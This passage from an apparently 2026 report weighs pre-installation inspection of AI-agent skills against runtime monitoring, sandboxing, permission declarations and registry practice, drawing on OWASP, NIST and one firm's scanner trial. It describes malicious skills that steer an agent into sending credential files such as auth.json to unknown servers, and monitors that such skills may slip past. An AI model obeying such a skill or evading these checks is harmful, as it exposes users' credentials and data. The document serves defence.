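A network block does not depend on how anyone interprets the skill, so it can stop the backup that both models accepted. But if the user approves the backup's destination because a model classified the skill as safe, the block depends on that classification.

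### What each side can tell the other

An inspector's findings can become a runtime policy. OWASP's *Agentic Skills Top 10* (2026), voluntary guidance from a software-security nonprofit, proposes a standard format in which each skill declares its permissions. The file organiser's declaration might contain:

```
permissions:
  files:
    read:  [~/Downloads]
    write: [~/Downloads]
  network:
    deny: "*"
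  shell: true
```

Before installation, an inspector checks whether a file organiser needs the permissions it declares and whether `organise.py` stays within them. During use, a sandbox or reference monitor enforces those permissions, so an upload they don't allow fails even if the inspector missed it. OWASP recommends this enforcement and also recommends comparing the declaration with what the skill does in a test run. Neither measure helps much with a tool like the fake Postmark server, which needed the dangerous permission to do its job.

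The inspection verdict also has to apply to the files the agent actually loads, which checks at submission do not guarantee, according to *Sealing the Audit-Runtime Gap for LLM Skills* (2026). *ClawGuard* (2026) describes a runtime framework in which a language model inspects each skill before its first use and again only if the skill's content changes.

A runtime alarm can also guide inspection. Suppose a monitor stops a file organiser from sending `auth.json` to an unknown server. The trace shows an inspector the type of file that triggered the transfer and the server's address, details that may not have come up in a test run. The inspector can then look for the rule responsible and search other skills for the same address. This second inspection is important because many runtime alarms are false, and a registry that removed skills based on an alarm alone would remove harmless ones.

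If the skill turns out to be malicious, OWASP's checklist includes isolating the affected agents, revoking exposed credentials, notifying the registry and updating detection signatures. One user's alarm can then protect everyone who has not yet installed the skill. Removing the skill from the registry does not delete installed copies, so OWASP advises companies to keep an inventory of their skills with versions and hashes. Registries also need to share their findings. OWASP reports that the same accounts published malicious skills on two registries, ClawHub and skills.sh, which did not share scanning results.

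### Time, lost functions and attention

Inspection mostly uses resources once per version, whereas runtime measures use them with every action. Truong-Le and colleagues' reasoning system took a median of 109 seconds per skill on eight data-centre processors, not counting the test run, but a user could rely on that result until the skill changed. *SkillShield* (2026) describes a lighter runtime measure, a set of written security instructions that the agent keeps in its context. These add about 2,400 tokens, or 2.4 to 12 per cent of a ten-step session, and require no second model. A monitor outside the agent uses more resources because it has to check the actions separately, but the agent cannot ignore it as it might ignore written instructions.

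Restrictions also make the agent less useful. CaMeL, for example, blocked about a quarter of the legitimate AgentDojo tasks in one test. Similarly, a false alarm before installation makes the user go without a harmless skill or wait for a review.

A small field report from one firm, Workloft, shows how much time reviewing a scanner's alarms can take. In *Skills are the new npm install, so we scanned ours*, Alfred and Bob (2026) ran SkillSpector, without its language model, on 107 skills, plugins and sets of configuration files. The scan took less than six minutes and produced 276 findings rated high or critical. They read all 276 and found nothing malicious. Seven findings were accurate; for example, two older skills told the agent to read a credentials file directly. The rest were false alarms, some caused by the firm's own security rules, which contained the patterns they were meant to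 block. At ten minutes each, reading the findings would take 46 hours. A single rule about bundled dependencies produced another 5,174 alarms, which the firm set aside without review.

If the scanner had been used to approve installations, it would have blocked 41 of the 107 harmless items. It also blocked nine of ten malicious skills that the firm had written as a test, though ten is too few to estimate its recall precisely. Workloft now treats a block as a request for human review, and its daily scan raises an alert only for findings that nobody has reviewed, which means much of the work is done only once. Without such a filter, people may stop taking the alerts seriously. *SkillGate* (2026) warns that wrongly blocking skills erodes developers' trust.

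Reviewers' time can easily cost more than the computing. If one skill in a hundred needed ten minutes from a reviewer paid $50 an hour, this would add about 8 cents to the average cost per skill, roughly 14 times what Hou and Yang's models cost.

### A registry, a company and an individual

| Check | Registry | Company | Individual |
|---|---|---|---|
| Static scan | Every skill and update | Every skill before approval | Each skill they want to install |
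| Model review | Suspicious skills | Suspicious skills | Affordable at a few cents a skill |
| Test run | Riskiest skills, with a few common models | With its own model and typical files | Rarely practical |
| Containment | Not possible on users' machines | Can require it for all staff | Can switch on the agent's sandbox |
| Monitoring | Depends on users' reports | Logs and a security team | The agent's built-in checks |
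| Removal | From the catalogue | From all its machines | From their own machine |

A registry's operators can compare all its skills and publishers, but they can't see which models or files its users have. Their main difficulty is the number of skills. ClawHub grew from 33,399 to 65,175 skills in 91 days, according to Xiong and Zhang, and at least one of its three scanners flagged 24,148 of them. At ten minutes each, reviewing the flagged skills would take about 4,000 hours, or two years for one full-time employee. Users do little of the reviewing, since 78 per cent of the skills had no stars or comments. Starting with popular skills would help, because the most-downloaded tenth accounted for 47 per cent of downloads. Popular skills can still be malicious. OWASP reports that at the peak of one campaign, five of ClawHub's seven most-downloaded skills were malware. It asks registries to scan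 every skill, verify publishers, warn users about risky permissions and remove malicious skills quickly.

A company can run every check in the table on its own combination of model, skills and files. OWASP asks companies to approve skills before installation, log what the skills do, give agents limited credentials, and have a procedure for withdrawing a skill. It also suggests keeping an internal copy of the registry that contains only approved skills.

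US government guidance deals more with what happens once agents are running. NIST, NSA and CISA's *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response* (2026) lists ten voluntary practices, such as testing the monitors themselves, preserving evidence and strengthening containment before restarting an agent. OpenAI's agents got back online within days of a restart, which shows why that last practice is needed. The list is mainly for organisations that train or evaluate highly capable agents, but may also apply to companies that deploy them. It covers incidents in which neither the operator nor an attacker told the agent to act. It would not cover an agent that obeyed a malicious skill, so a company also needs guidance like OWASP's.

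NIST's other work on agents is at an earlier stage. The draft *Adversarial Machine Learning* (Hamin, 2026) sets out common terms for attacks and ways of mitigating them, which later standards can use. It focuses on agent systems and is open for comment until 18 December (NIST, 2026). NIST has also proposed separate sets of security controls for single agents and for groups of agents.

OWASP asks individuals to install skills only from trusted publishers, check permissions, review their installed skills occasionally, report suspicious behaviour and keep the agent software up to date. Most people cannot judge a scanner's findings as a security team can, but they can still use one. Someone who wants a file organiser can scan a candidate in a few seconds, pick another if the scanner flags it, and run the chosen one on a copy of the folder in a sandbox without network access.
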